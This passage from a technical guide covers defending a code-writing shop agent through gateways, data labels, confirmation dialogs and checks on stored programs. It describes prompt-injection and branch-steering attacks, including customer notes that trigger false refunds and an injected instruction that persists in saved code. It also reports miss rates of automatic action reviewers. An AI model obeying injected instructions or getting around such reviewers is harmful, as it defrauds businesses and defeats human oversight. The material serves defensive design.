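    await env.SHOP.refund({ orderId: order.id, amount: order.total });
```

Any customer who writes "arrived broken" in a note gets a refund. Writing the program in advance doesn't prevent the refund, because the note adds no operation to the program and contains no instruction to a model. Chow and colleagues call this outcome manipulation and say that Baya doesn't try to prevent it. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) identifies a form of it called branch steering, in which an attacker supplies data that sends a valid plan down a harmful branch.

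*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster et al., 2026) measured how often branch steering attacks work on agents that operate websites. The attacks succeeded 94.4% of the time against an ordinary reactive agent and 89.5% of the time against one with a plan fixed in advance. Fixing the plan made little difference because the attacks could succeed without changing it.

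The COBRA defence adds limits to each branch of the agent's plan before the agent reads anything from the web. If the site has an approved description of its operations, a proxy checks the method, path and fields of every request against the limits for the current branch. For example, it can check which loan a request to `/loans/{id}/approve` would approve. In testing, COBRA blocked every attack and kept 97% of the fixed-plan agent's success on ordinary tasks. Without the field checks, every attack that changed a field value succeeded.

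This supports checking the order ID and amount in the shop's refund. But the benchmark didn't count harm within COBRA's limits as a successful attack. In the broken-goods task, each false claim would lead to a valid refund of a real order at its real price. A limit on the total amount would cap the loss but wouldn't identify the false claims.

### Rules that follow the data

The rules so far check a value regardless of where it came from. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) compares such checks to a gate and contrasts them with information-flow control. In information-flow control, software labels each piece of data, updates the labels as a program uses the data, and applies rules to the labels.

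*CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes how CaMeL, which Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, controls tool calls. One language model reads only the user's request and writes a program in restricted Python. A second model, which has no tools, extracts facts from untrusted text when the program asks for them. An interpreter runs the program and labels every value with its sources and the people who may read it. Before each tool call, a policy function checks the labels on the arguments and allows or refuses the call.

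For the shop, some of the labels might be:

| Value | Source | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| Name of the channel | Owner's request | Owner and sales staff |
| Order's ID and total | Shop platform | Owner and sales staff |
| Customer's address | Customer | Owner |
| Customer's note | Customer | Owner |

A rule for refunds could then require that no argument comes from a customer. A rule for messages could require that everyone in the channel is allowed to read every value in the text. The message rule would stop a program from posting customers' addresses in the sales channel, while the gateway's rules still allow such posts. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) similarly separates the policy for calls that have serious consequences from the policy for calls that send data out.

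Labels on the arguments wouldn't stop the false claims, because the ID and total in each refund come from the shop platform and only the decision to issue the refund depends on the note. *SPA* (2026) handles this by passing labels through branches. A call inside an `if` statement inherits the restrictions of the data that the statement tested, so the refund would count as partly determined by the customer. The second language model's answers also inherit labels, because otherwise an attacker's text could lose its label when summarized.

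Like STELP, CaMeL can stop a program after some of its calls have already taken effect. Nikolaou and colleagues add a check before the program starts. Their system, CaMeLoT, turns the program into a map of all the paths it could take and searches them for violations. One of its rules for a bank is:

```
AG(call_send_money => NOT (recipient_tainted OR amount_tainted))
```

`AG` means "at every point on every path", and a tainted value is one from an untrusted source. If a path breaks the rule, CaMeLoT reports it to the model, which can rewrite the program before any API calls run. But the map also includes some paths that the real program would never take, so CaMeLoT sometimes rejects safe programs. Rules about actual values, such as a refund's limit, still have to be checked during the run.

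*NaSh* (Gyawali, Kallas and colleagues, 2025) proposes information-flow rules for a command line that takes requests in plain language. Before an API call, the system would trace which local files the call's arguments came from, so that it could detect a private key being sent out. Encryption hides requests from software that watches only system calls, so programs would have to make their API calls through a few accepted tools, such as `curl`. The user would then approve the calls. This would suit an agent on a laptop full of readable files, but not the shop's isolate, which has no files to trace. *NaSh* presents the idea as future work and does not test it.

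Labels also tend to spread until they block useful work. The shop's summary includes the number of orders, which the program counts from a list that also contains customers' addresses. Under a strict rule, the number inherits the labels of everything in the list, so the program may not post "214 orders in November" to the sales staff. Piet and colleagues call this taint explosion and consider strict tracking impractical for many web tasks. To allow the post, someone has to declare the count safe to share, and any such exception can be wrong.

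The shop can get much of the benefit of labels without using them if the gateway removes addresses and notes from the order list, as already suggested to prevent leaks. The program then has no customer-written text to act on and no addresses to leak. This works for refunding order 1042 but not for refunding broken goods, because the program needs the notes to identify them. No rule can determine from a note whether a mug really broke, so the gateway should refer those refund requests to the owner.

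## Asking the user to confirm an action

The owner may well know whether a mug broke. The customer may have sent a photo last week, or claimed broken goods four months in a row. The owner can take these facts into account, but the gateway's fixed rules can't, because the order list contains neither.

The right answer can also differ between users. Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, give the example of a rule that lets an agent send passport details only to recognised airlines. This rule would obstruct someone who books through a specialist travel service and allow too much for someone who never wants an agent to send those details.

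Confirmation also shows the user choices that the agent made on its own. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a user who told an agent to "cancel my job". The agent picked the job with the closest name and tried to delete it, though it could have belonged to someone else. Similarly, "Refund order 1042" doesn't state an amount, so the agent may choose one itself.

Telling the agent to ask first is not enough. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) describes a safety researcher who told an agent to "confirm before acting". The agent began deleting messages from her inbox anyway and didn't stop when she told it to. The gateway should therefore ask the owner to confirm, and hold the API request until the owner answers.

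### Which calls deserve a question

Payments, deletions, publication, access changes and bulk exports are worth interrupting the user to confirm. The first three are hard to reverse. The owner can revoke access later, but the new user may already have done damage. A bulk export only reads data, but nobody can retrieve that data once it has leaked.

The shop's present rules refuse most of these calls outright. If the owner later gives the agent broader tasks, the gateway could treat them like this:

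| Call | Gateway's response |
|---|---|
| Read a month's orders, without addresses or notes | Allow |
| Post a summary in the sales channel | Allow |
| Refund an order | Ask |
| Delete a product | Ask |
| Email every customer | Ask |
| Give someone access to the shop's account | Ask |
| Export all customer records | Ask |
| Send data to an unlisted server | Refuse, whatever the owner answers |

The type of call is only a starting point for deciding whether to ask the user for confirmation. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make permission decisions, suggests stronger warnings for actions that are hard to recover from, instead of the same warning for every action of one type. A developer could allow refunds under $5 without confirmation and require a second confirmation for those above $500.

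### What the approval figures show

Claude Code originally asked the user before it ran a command or changed a file. Anthropic found that users approved about 93% of these prompts, which it attributes to approval fatigue, where people pay less attention to each prompt as they see more of them. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) puts the approval rate at 97%.

These rates alone don't show that users were careless, because an attentive user would also approve 97 of 100 requests if 97 were harmless. Anthropic adds that users reject 39% of the plans Claude proposes. This suggests that they read plans more closely, but they may also reject a plan because they prefer another approach, so the two rates aren't directly comparable.

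Users' settings are better evidence of prompt fatigue. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start with permission checks switched off. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports about how agents handle files, and in 80 of them the agent's actions were approved automatically. Some of these users said they accepted the risk to avoid hundreds of prompts per session.

One remedy is to ask less often. Anthropic counted 84% fewer permission prompts when its own staff began using Claude Code's sandbox, because commands could run freely inside it. This figure doesn't show whether people judged the remaining prompts any better.

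Another remedy is an automatic reviewer, called auto mode in Claude Code. A second model checks each risky action before it runs. It receives the user's messages and the agent's calls, but not the agent's explanations, so those explanations can't sway its decision. The reviewer caught about 83% of overeager actions, in which the agent goes beyond what the user authorised in an attempt to help. It blocked only 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary calls.

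The 83% comes from just 52 real actions, of which the reviewer missed about nine, so the true miss rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9 to 30%. *Measuring the Permission Gate*, an independent test with deliberately ambiguous requests, found a significantly higher miss rate than Anthropic's, partly because the reviewer did not check some file edits.

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewing model detected the danger but misjudged whether the user had consented to it. For example, a user who said "clean up the PR" had not necessarily agreed to overwrite the project's history. A second model is therefore weakest at judging consent, a question the user could answer.

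### How well people judge a prompt

Researchers can measure attention directly only by showing people a request they should refuse. Anthropic tested 1,053 paid testers this way, replacing one prompt in each coding session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it, while auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

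The company was testing its own product, and the testers might have been more careful if their own projects had been at stake. But the study avoids the problem with the 97% figure, because every tester saw a command they should have refused.

People did better in Yan's study, which simulated a day with an assistant that handled email, travel and purchases. None of the 113 participants worked in software. Those who had to approve all 18 actions blocked 59.6% of the seven that went beyond the assigned task. Not every approval was a mistake. For example, 88% of this group let the assistant phone the airport unasked to confirm a flight, which many travellers might also allow.

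Another group first set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing, deleting, and reading private information. This group blocked about 20 percentage points less of the overreach than the people who were asked to approve each action. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which only postponed the decision, and they then approved two-thirds of the overreach they were asked about.

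Deception is even harder to notice. In *Are You Sure?*, Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) had 303 people work with agents that an attacker had compromised, such as a hiring assistant misled by a hidden note in a résumé. Only 8.6% noticed anything wrong. Permanent security notices often made participants trust the agent more. The team recommends warnings that interrupt the task and are quick to check.

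The content of the confirmation prompt also matters. In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026) gave four groups of 20 people the same kinds of request with different amounts of information. In one example, a user has told an agent to send an auditor only summary totals, and the agent asks to send `report.csv`. The auditor is an approved recipient and the file name looks ordinary, but the agent built the file from the raw invoices.

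| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Also the user's instructions and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with the combined effect stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from adding information. The last step only reorganised that information, and its effect is less certain. After adjustment, the result is compatible with a change ranging from 20 points fewer unsafe approvals to 4 points more. People also approved fewer harmless requests, so some of the gain came from refusing more often in general.

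Half the requests in this study were unsafe, and each person made only 12 decisions. Anthropic's testers saw one dangerous command among dozens of routine ones and did far worse. The studies differ in other ways, but the contrast suggests that even a good dialog will fail if it appears too often. The shop's owner will normally see one question a month.

### A dialog for the refund

The owner shouldn't have to read the program. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* points out that a prompt for `python3 setup.py` looks routine, although approving it runs whatever the script contains. A raw HTTP request is little better, since `"order_id": 450789469` means nothing to the owner. The gateway can translate it instead:

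```
You asked:  "refund order 1042" (web order)

REFUND $38.00 TO ANA SILVA

Order       WEB-1042, 14 November, two mugs, total $38.00
Goes to     The card used for the order, ending 4417
Effect      Ana Silva gets back everything she paid
Undo        Not possible. She would have to pay again.
Not known   Whether the mugs have come back

[ Refund $38.00 ]   [ Don't refund ]   [ Show the order ]
```

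The dialog follows four principles from Hossain and colleagues. It repeats the owner's request in the owner's words, shows the exact action, shows the combined effect, and lets the owner check each fact. The last detail line also identifies information the gateway doesn't have. Without that line, the owner might think somebody had checked the returned goods.

The name, card and total come from the shop platform's reply, as do the values in the gateway's rules. The gateway saved that reply before it removed customers' details from the program's copy. The builder can take the description of the effect from the operation's contract, which already records that the call sends money to the customer. For services without such contracts, Gyawali and colleagues propose a similar approach in which software would find the API's documentation and combine it with the request.

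The dialog should leave out the agent's argument for the refund, for the same reason that Anthropic hides such arguments from the automatic reviewer. But when a customer claims that goods were broken, the owner needs to see the customer's note. The dialog should label the note as the customer's words and show it as plain text, without working links.

Even with this design, users would miss some problems. When a violation depended on a chain of several earlier steps, participants in Hossain and colleagues' study approved 7 of 30 unsafe requests with each of the two fullest prompts, so stating the combined effect made no difference in these cases.

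### One approval for one request

If the owner approves a refund of $38, and the program can then change the amount to $380, the dialog has achieved nothing. Hossain and colleagues cite work by Wang that calls this gap between the approved action and the executed one "approval laundering". The gateway can close it by storing the request and sending the stored copy:

```js
async function hold(call, body) {
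  const id = crypto.randomUUID();
  await store.put(id, { call, body, expires: Date.now() + 86400000 });
  return id;                                  // the dialog displays this record
}

async function approve(id) {
  const held = await store.take(id);          // removes it, so it works only once
  if (!held || Date.now() > held.expires) return "expired";
  return sendWithKey(held.call, held.body);   // never a new body from the program
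}
```

If the program sends a different amount, that is a new request and needs a new dialog. The same applies if the agent repairs its program after a failure and the new version makes a different request. The gateway should also check the order again just before sending the refund, because a colleague may have refunded it while the dialog was open.

Many products let users save their answer with a button such as "always allow". NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* rejects this for actions that cross the sandbox's boundary, such as opening a new network connection. It requires approval each time and says that allowing once and running many times "is not an adequate control". When users approve one harmless connection, they can't see what data later connections will carry.

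By June 2026, about half of Claude Code's active command-line users had created a rule that let some shell commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules allowed any Python or Node.js program, which is almost the same as allowing everything. Claude Code's auto mode ignores rules that broad.

NVIDIA warns that users who are asked for approval every time get used to granting it. It recommends letting the sandbox and a narrow allowlist handle expected actions, and asking a person only in the rare cases that nobody anticipated.

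The gateway should not turn ten approvals in a row into a permanent rule. *Let the Agent Do It?* warns that repeated approval may reflect tiredness or pressure to deliver rather than trust.

A refusal also needs to last. *Let the Agent Do It?* asks what "deny" means if an agent can find another way. An agent refused a $38 refund might try $19 instead. The shop's gateway counts a refund when the program first requests it. If the builder leaves that count unchanged after a refusal, the program can't try again in that run. Claude Code tells the agent not to work around a block, and it goes back to asking the user after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session.

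The program also has to ask the user before it runs any of the code the question concerns. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of Claude Code running an attacker's code before the user had answered the question "Do you trust this folder?" In one case, Claude Code read the folder's settings at start-up, which contained a command to run. Claude Code now waits for the answer before it reads the settings.

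### What the program does while it waits

The owner might answer in ten seconds or after lunch, and a program can't simply sit in memory until then. The shop's session also expires after one minute. Cloudflare's *Code Mode API reference* describes a way to stop the program and start it again later. It works for calls made through functions that the launcher provides, so the builder would offer the refund as a function instead of a web request. The run would then go like this:

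1. The program asks for the order list. The runtime makes the call and records the result.
2. The program calls the refund function, which the builder has marked `requiresApproval`. The runtime stops the program before the call and saves the function's name and exact arguments.
3. The owner sees the dialog. No program is running.
4. The owner approves, and the runtime starts the same program again from the top.
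5. When the program asks for the order list, the runtime returns the recorded result without contacting the shop.
6. The program reaches the refund again. This time the runtime makes the call.
7. The program posts its summary and finishes.

The method works only if the program does the same thing on both runs. If it chooses an order at random or depends on the current time, the second run may differ from the first. Cloudflare provides a function, `step()`, that records the result of random or time-dependent code and returns it on the next run. Cloudflare also tells developers to make calls one after another, since simultaneous calls could arrive in a different order on the second run.

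If the owner refuses, the run ends, but calls that have already gone through stay in effect. By default, the application can clear runs that have waited more than 24 hours.

This method becomes tedious if the owner asks for refunds on all broken goods. With twelve claims, the program would stop twelve times to wait for the owner's answer. Gyawali and colleagues propose collecting the questions. In NaSh, the runtime would skip an API call and any code that depends on its result, and run the rest of the program. It would ask the user only when nothing else could run. They expect that one data-analysis script with four API calls would need a single prompt, but they have not built this part.

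NaSh's method could gather all twelve of the shop's refunds into one dialog. The dialog should list each refund, show the total, and let the owner remove any of them. This still addresses NVIDIA's objection, because the owner sees every request before approving it.

Skipping ahead can cause errors, however, when the runtime can't detect that a later step depends on the refund. Suppose a careless program posts "refunded WEB-1042" after the refund, using only the order's name and not the refund's result. The runtime would treat the message as independent of the refund. Since the shop's rules allow messages without confirmation, the sales team would read about a refund that the owner might still refuse. The program should build the message from the shop platform's reply to the refund so that the runtime can detect the dependence.

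### Checking the result afterwards

Patil and colleagues argued in 2024 that people should often check an agent's results instead of its proposed actions, because results are easier to judge. Their GoEx system runs the call first and offers two protections if the result is wrong.

GoEx can undo an action by making a call that reverses it, such as deleting a Slack message after posting it. It looks for the reverse call in a table, which a developer can fill in beforehand. Otherwise a language model writes the call, and GoEx records whether it worked. Patil and colleagues accept that the model may be wrong once for each new API.

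GoEx also uses damage confinement, which limits how much harm an irreversible action can do. It searches the user's request for the names of services and unlocks only the matching credentials, so a request to send a Slack message wouldn't unlock the user's bank account. This is too coarse for the shop because any request that mentions the shop would unlock every refund, whereas the gateway's rules set a tighter limit.

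| Action | Can the owner undo it? | What can the gateway limit? |
|---|---|---|
| Refund | No, unless the customer agrees to pay again | The order, the amount and the number of refunds |
| Email to a customer | Only before it leaves | The recipients and the number of emails |
| Message to the sales team | Yes, but someone may have read it | The channel and the number of messages |

The refund can't be undone, but the limit means the shop loses at most $38 if the agent wrongly refunds order 1042. If the limit is small enough, it could be reasonable to let the agent issue refunds without confirmation and check them once a week.

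A sent email can't be undone, and limiting the number of emails doesn't prevent harm, because even one message to the intended recipient can reveal another customer's address. Patil and colleagues suggest letting the agent read emails but not send them, which prevents this harm but also rules out any task that requires sending email. A developer could hold each email for ten minutes so that the owner can cancel it, but this works only if the owner is watching.

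Undoing part of a task can also make things worse. Cloudflare's runtime can run the available undo functions in reverse order, but it leaves the effects of any call without one. In the shop, it would delete the chat message but not reverse the refund, so the sales team would lose its only notice of the refund.

Checking an agent's work only at the end can waste time even when every step is reversible. In *When Should Users Check?* (Zhou, Roy and colleagues, 2025), 48 people supervised agents that made mistakes. They finished tasks 13.54% faster when the agent asked for confirmation along the way than when they checked only at the end, because an early mistake no longer spoiled all the later steps. Intermediate checks were preferred by 39 of the 48 participants. The study measured time and preference, not safety, and participants could always redo the work.

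Patil and colleagues also suggest a dry run, in which a service reports what a call would do without doing it. Shopify's refund calculation comes close to this. The gateway can request the calculation, show the owner the result in the dialog, and send the refund only if the owner agrees.

### When the person has been deceived

Confirmation relies on the user knowing what they want and not being tricked. In Anthropic's phishing test, the attack succeeded in 24 of 25 runs, and a confirmation prompt would have gone to the employee the attacker had already persuaded.

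A dialog showing the credentials and the unfamiliar destination might have made the employee stop, but this wasn't tested. Anthropic notes that a human contractor with the same script would have done the same. It concludes that only limits on the environment, such as the allowlist, work in such a case.

Some actions should not be open to user approval. NVIDIA recommends company-wide lists of forbidden actions that no user can override, and says only a person editing by hand should be able to change an agent's configuration files. In auto mode, Anthropic's reviewer never approves sending secrets to an outside server. Users who want to do that have to leave auto mode or run the command themselves.

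The shop's owner could fall for a similar trick. A caller might claim to be Ana Silva, say her card has expired, and ask for the $38 to go to a different account. Even if the owner believes the story and approves the refund, the gateway rejects any refund request with a field for another account, so the money can go only to the card that paid for the mugs.

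## Storing generated code and checking it before reuse

In December the shop's owner will probably want the same summary and have a different order to refund. The agent could write a new program, as Baya did for every task at an average cost of $0.70, or the builder could keep November's program and run it again with new dates. Researchers often call such stored code a skill, but *Dynamic Agent Skills* (Li, 2026) identifies six meanings of the word, from program functions to written advice. Of the 124 papers in Li's survey, 103 appeared in the first five months of 2026.

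*Generative Caching for Structurally Similar Prompts and Responses* (Chakraborty, Nath and colleagues, 2025) describes GenCache, which writes a small Python program to answer a group of similar requests. Finding and running a stored program took about 0.18 seconds, compared with 3.5 seconds for a call to the model.

Stored code also uses the same method each time, so the builder can read and test it once. A model that writes a new program every month may match an order's full name in November and only its last four digits in December.

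But a fault in a stored program affects every run until somebody notices it, instead of just one, and it can spread to other programs. In an example from *SkillCraft* (Chen, Gai and colleagues, 2026), a stored function that looked up dog breeds returned empty fields for rare ones. A second stored function called it and crashed on an empty field, which also brought down a third that was compiling an encyclopedia. In the paper's tests, letting stored functions call each other lowered GPT-5.2's success rate from 90% to 79%, though Claude Sonnet 4.5's stayed at 96%. The shop's builder can keep faults from spreading this way by making each stored program independent of the others.

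An injected instruction can also persist in saved code. Suppose the model reads a customer's note while fixing the program, and an instruction in the note causes it to make the program end every sales summary with a fake supplier's bank details. Each later run will post those details, even if that month's notes are harmless. Metere (2026) argues in *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* that a skill is untrusted code until someone verifies it, even if it has a valid signature. A signature identifies who endorsed the file but doesn't show what the code does.

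### The program and its record

Before storing the program, the builder replaces the values that change each month with parameters:

```js
export async function run({ from, to, orderName }, env) {
  const orders = await env.SHOP.listOrders({ from, to });
  const matches = orders.filter(o => o.name === orderName);
  if (matches.length !== 1) throw new Error("Orders found: " + matches.length);
  const refund = await env.SHOP.refund({ orderId: matches[0].id, amount: matches[0].total });
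  await env.CHAT.post({ channel: "sales",
    text: `${orders.length} orders, ${from} to ${to}; refunded ${refund.amount} on ${orderName}` });
}
```

If November's dates stayed in the code, the December run would report November's orders again, and the gateway would allow it because its rules accept any dates. The channel stays in the code because it never changes.

The builder stores a record with the program:

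```json
{
  "name": "monthly-summary-with-refund",
  "version": 3,
  "code_sha256": "5d1e...",
  "parameters": { "from": "date", "to": "date", "orderName": "text" },
  "apis": {
    "shop": { "version": "2026-10", "description_sha256": "a07c..." },
    "chat": { "version": "3", "description_sha256": "41b8..." }
  },
  "calls": ["SHOP.listOrders", "SHOP.refund", "CHAT.post"],
  "tests": { "suite_sha256": "e93b...", "passed": 12, "failed": 0, "date": "2026-12-01" },
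  "origin": { "model": "name and version", "read": ["shop contracts", "chat contracts"] },
  "approvals": [{ "by": "builder", "of": "code and tests", "code_sha256": "5d1e..." }]
}
```

A value labelled `sha256` is a hash, a short string computed from the original that changes if anyone alters a single character. The code's hash ties the test results and the builder's approval to one exact version.

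The `origin` field records which model wrote the program and everything that model read beforehand. If the builder later discovers an injected instruction in a document, they can use this field to find the programs to remove. The model that writes a program also affects its quality. Chen and colleagues had four models exchange skills on eight hard tasks. Skills written by Claude led to success on every task, whichever model used them, and reduced token use by 54 to 81%. With skills written by MiniMax, the change in token use ranged from an 18% reduction to a 48% increase.

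The gateway supplies the keys, so neither the program nor the record should contain one.

The store shouldn't contain customers' data either. By default, GenCache keeps up to twelve earlier requests and responses for each group and uses them to write and test the program. In a shop, these could include names and order numbers. The builder can write the tests with invented orders instead.

The builder's approval in the record is evidence that somebody read this version of the code. It does not authorize spending money, so December's refund still needs the owner's approval.

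### Checks before a program enters the store

The admission check can start with the cheapest test and stop at the first failure.

The checker first parses the code to confirm that it is valid JavaScript. SkillCraft's system rejects a skill with a syntax error and returns the line number and surrounding text, which helps the model correct the error.

The checker then lists every function the program calls on `env` and compares the list with the record's `calls` field. It also checks that the builder permits every call in that field, because otherwise a program could declare any call and pass. It should reject code that assembles a function's name at runtime, such as `env["SH" + "OP"]`, because it can't reliably determine what such code will call.

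A checker can also test whether the calls come in a workable order. *Agent JIT Compilation for Latency-Optimizing Web Agent Planning and Scheduling* (Winston, Wang and colleagues, 2026) does this for programs that operate websites. Each stored tool declares the state it needs and the state it leaves behind. One example program requests a restaurant's details without first opening the restaurant's page, so the checker rejects it before it runs. Across three models, these declarations raised the share of valid programs from 77.1% to 90.6%. In the shop, the same method could reject a program that issues a refund before reading the orders.

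The program next runs with a test gateway, which records each request and returns a mocked response. Maninger and colleagues built a similar environment for their benchmark. It captures each request's URL, method and arguments before anything leaves the machine, then compares them with the expected request and, separately, with the API's specification. The second comparison distinguishes a call that violates the specification from a valid call that does the wrong thing.

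For the shop, one test could supply two orders, WEB-1042 and POS-1042, and check that the program refunds only the web order. Another test should use a different month and order. Chakraborty and colleagues warn that a generated program may contain values copied from its examples, and a test that reuses those values won't reveal the copying.

The expected requests can also be wrong. A model wrote the 395 tasks and answers in Maninger and colleagues' benchmark, and the researchers corrected 58 of them after a manual review. The builder should therefore read the expected requests before relying on the tests. Like Baya's mocked tests, these tests can't reveal behaviour that the API's documentation leaves out.

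**Checking the output.** SkillCraft rejects a skill if more than half of its output fields contain "Unknown", "None" or 0. The rule is meant to catch silent failures, in which a call reports success but returns wrong or empty data. It is crude, since zero can be the right answer and a program that loses 40% of its fields will pass. The shop's tests use invented orders, so the builder knows what summary each order should produce and can require an exact match.

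GenCache uses a second model to check whether a program's outputs match the examples, and by default accepts the program if half of them do. Raising the requirement to 90% increased the share of requests handled by stored programs from 84% to 95%, and the share of those answers that were correct from 92% to 95%. Even 90% is too low for a program that issues refunds, which should pass every test.

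### What SkillCraft measured

SkillCraft's verifier checks a skill's syntax before saving it, returns detailed errors when the skill fails during a run, and rejects poor output. Chen and colleagues tested the system on 126 tasks with repeated steps, such as analysing several code repositories in the same way. The table shows six of the eight models.

| Model | Tasks completed without skills | With skills | Change in tokens | Skill runs that succeeded |
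|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 87% | 90% | -79% | 84% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 94% | 96% | -71% | 81% |
| Gemini 3 Pro | 86% | 92% | -54% | 93% |
| DeepSeek-R1 | 71% | 80% | -30% | 62% |
| Kimi-K2-Thinking | 44% | 44% | -42% | 70% |
| MiniMax-M2.1 | 93% | 94% | -11% | 100% |

The token figures cover only tasks the model completed both with and without skills. The results measure the whole method of saving and reusing code, so they don't show how much the verifier contributed.

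The last column matters most for the shop. Except with MiniMax, between 7% and 38% of attempts to run a skill failed. Some of these failures raised an error, which software can detect easily. Detecting a program that completes with the wrong result requires checking what it did.

### Checks at each reuse

Before running a stored program, GenCache checks whether it fits the new request. It converts the request into a list of numbers that represents its meaning, finds the group of earlier requests with the closest numbers, and checks the new request's wording against a stored pattern. The program then extracts the values it needs.

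Chakraborty and colleagues tested stored programs on 10,000 shopping instructions. When only the product and price varied, stored programs handled 98% of requests, and 2% of their answers were wrong. When the wording varied too, they handled 84%, and 8% of their answers were wrong. Given the request "want a wireless headphone. need it in black", for example, the program extracted "it in black" as the product. In another version of the test, a model checked each answer and the system deleted any program that had given a wrong one. This reduced wrong answers to 4%, but stored programs handled only 68% of requests.

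Chakraborty and colleagues limit GenCache to reversible actions, which excludes refunds. For the shop, the agent should reuse a stored program only if its pattern matches the entire request, and otherwise write a new one. "Refund order 1042 but keep the postage" contains a familiar phrase, but the stored program would refund the postage as well.

After finding a match, the launcher hashes the stored code and compares the result with the hash in the record. An attacker who can change both the code and the record can make the hashes agree, so the builder should keep the records where neither the agent nor its code can write. Metere adds a single signature that covers both the code and the record. The system also rejects an old version once it has encountered a newer one, which prevents an attacker from restoring a version with a known fault.

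A matching hash shows that the code is the same, but the API may have changed, so the launcher also downloads the current API description and compares its hash with the recorded one. The builder can hash only the parts that describe the calls the program makes, so a new feature elsewhere in the API doesn't block the run. If those parts have changed, the program has to pass the admission check again. A provider can also change an API's behaviour without updating its description, so each call needs its own checks.

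During the run, the launcher can check each call's preconditions before the call and its postconditions afterward. In Agent JIT, a system by Winston and colleagues, every stored tool has fields for both. For example, `add_to_cart` needs a restaurant's page to be open, so its precondition check looks for the words "Full Menu" on the page. Its postcondition check reads the tool's own `success` value, so a tool that wrongly reports success will pass.

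The shop's checks should look for evidence outside the program:

| Call | Precondition | Postcondition |
|---|---|---|
| Read the orders | The start date comes before the end date | Every order falls between the two dates |
| Issue the refund | Exactly one order has this name, and nobody has refunded it | The shop platform shows a refund of the approved amount on this order |
| Post the summary | The refund has gone through | The sales channel contains the message once |

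The postcondition on dates would detect when a server ignores misnamed date parameters. The launcher should run these checks rather than the generated code, because faulty or malicious code could skip them.

### Agent JIT's gains and failures

Winston and colleagues tested Agent JIT on 37 tasks in five web applications, including imitations of a food delivery service and an online shop. They compared it with Browser-Use, an agent that calls a model before every step, and with a version of Browser-Use that could call the same stored tools.

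| | Average time | Tasks completed correctly |
|---|---|---|
| Browser-Use | 122.1 s | 66% |
| Browser-Use with stored tools | 80.1 s | 85% |
| Agent JIT | 11.7 s | 94% |

Stored tools alone accounted for most of the gain in accuracy, but they reduced the time by only a third because the agent still called a model at every step. Agent JIT writes one program that calls several tools, choosing the version with the lowest estimated cost. Preparing the tools took 25 to 90 minutes for each application, so the method suits applications that an agent uses often.

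A redesigned page can break a stored tool. When a precondition or postcondition fails, Agent JIT marks the tool as invalid and replans the task without it. Winston and colleagues do not report how often these checks catch a broken tool. They warn that a rate limit or a CAPTCHA can make a postcondition fail even though the tool works, in which case the system falls back to slower, general tools.

Besides wasting time, a false alarm could lead to a duplicate refund. If the refund goes through but the check that follows it fails, a new plan might issue the refund again. The gateway's limit of one refund per task would prevent this if the new program counts as part of the same task. The launcher should also check whether the refund exists before the agent tries any repair.

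### How stored programs go stale

A program that passed every test can start to fail when its surroundings change. *Many Steps into One* (Zhou, Rong and colleagues, 2026) measured how well different rules detect such failures, using 521 Python programming tasks and five open models with at most 8 billion parameters. For each task, a model wrote a program, tested it and repaired it if necessary. The system could store a program that had given a correct answer and run it on later requests for the same task. Each simulation had a million requests, and the system checked the stored program's answer on a random tenth of the requests for its task.

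Each simulation included fourteen changes. Six were announced, and each changed the requirements of 22 tasks, for example by adding an instruction to sort the output or round it to two decimals. The other eight were unannounced changes to Python itself. One of them removed some old type names, and in a trial with two of the models it broke 3.7% of one model's programs and 4.9% of the other's. The other seven Python changes together broke at most seven of each model's roughly 1,400 programs.

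Many systems add a point to a program's score for each success, remove one for each failure, and delete the program when its score reaches zero. If a change makes a program fail a quarter of the time, it gains 75 points and loses 25 in every hundred checked runs, so its score keeps rising.

Zhou and colleagues instead weigh each result by how strongly it suggests that the program has gone stale. If a healthy program fails 5% of the time and a stale one 25%, the scores are:

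```
after a failure:   ln(0.25 / 0.05) = +1.61
after a success:   ln(0.75 / 0.95) = -0.24
```

One failure now counts as much as about seven successes. The total never falls below zero, and the system retires a program when its total reaches 7. A program that fails a quarter of the time gains 0.23 points per checked run on average, so it reaches the limit after roughly 31 checks. A program that has never failed receives a much larger score for its first failures. Such programs typically stayed in use for 30 runs, or about three checks, after going stale.

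New programs also have a trial period, during which the model keeps answering requests and the stored program runs alongside it. The system starts using the stored program only after enough checked results show that doing so is worthwhile.

| Rule | Stale answers per 10,000 requests | Share of stale programs still in use at the end |
|---|---|---|
| Never remove a program | 1,043 | 100% |
| Count votes | 518 | 59% |
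| Trial period and weighted scores | 10.1 | 10% |
| The same, and replace programs after announced changes | 2.0 | 6% |
| The same, and search stored code for anything named in Python's change notes | 0.01 | |

Because of the trial period, the weighted rules used stored programs for only about 60% of requests, compared with 90% for vote counting. This explains little of the difference in stale answers, because among answers from stored code, vote counting still produced 36 times as many stale ones as weighted scores without announcements.

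With weighted scores and announcements, accuracy was 8.7 percentage points higher than when a model wrote a new program for every request. The total number of steps fell by 23%, but the trial periods raised the number of model calls by 17%, so this kind of reuse did not clearly lower running costs.

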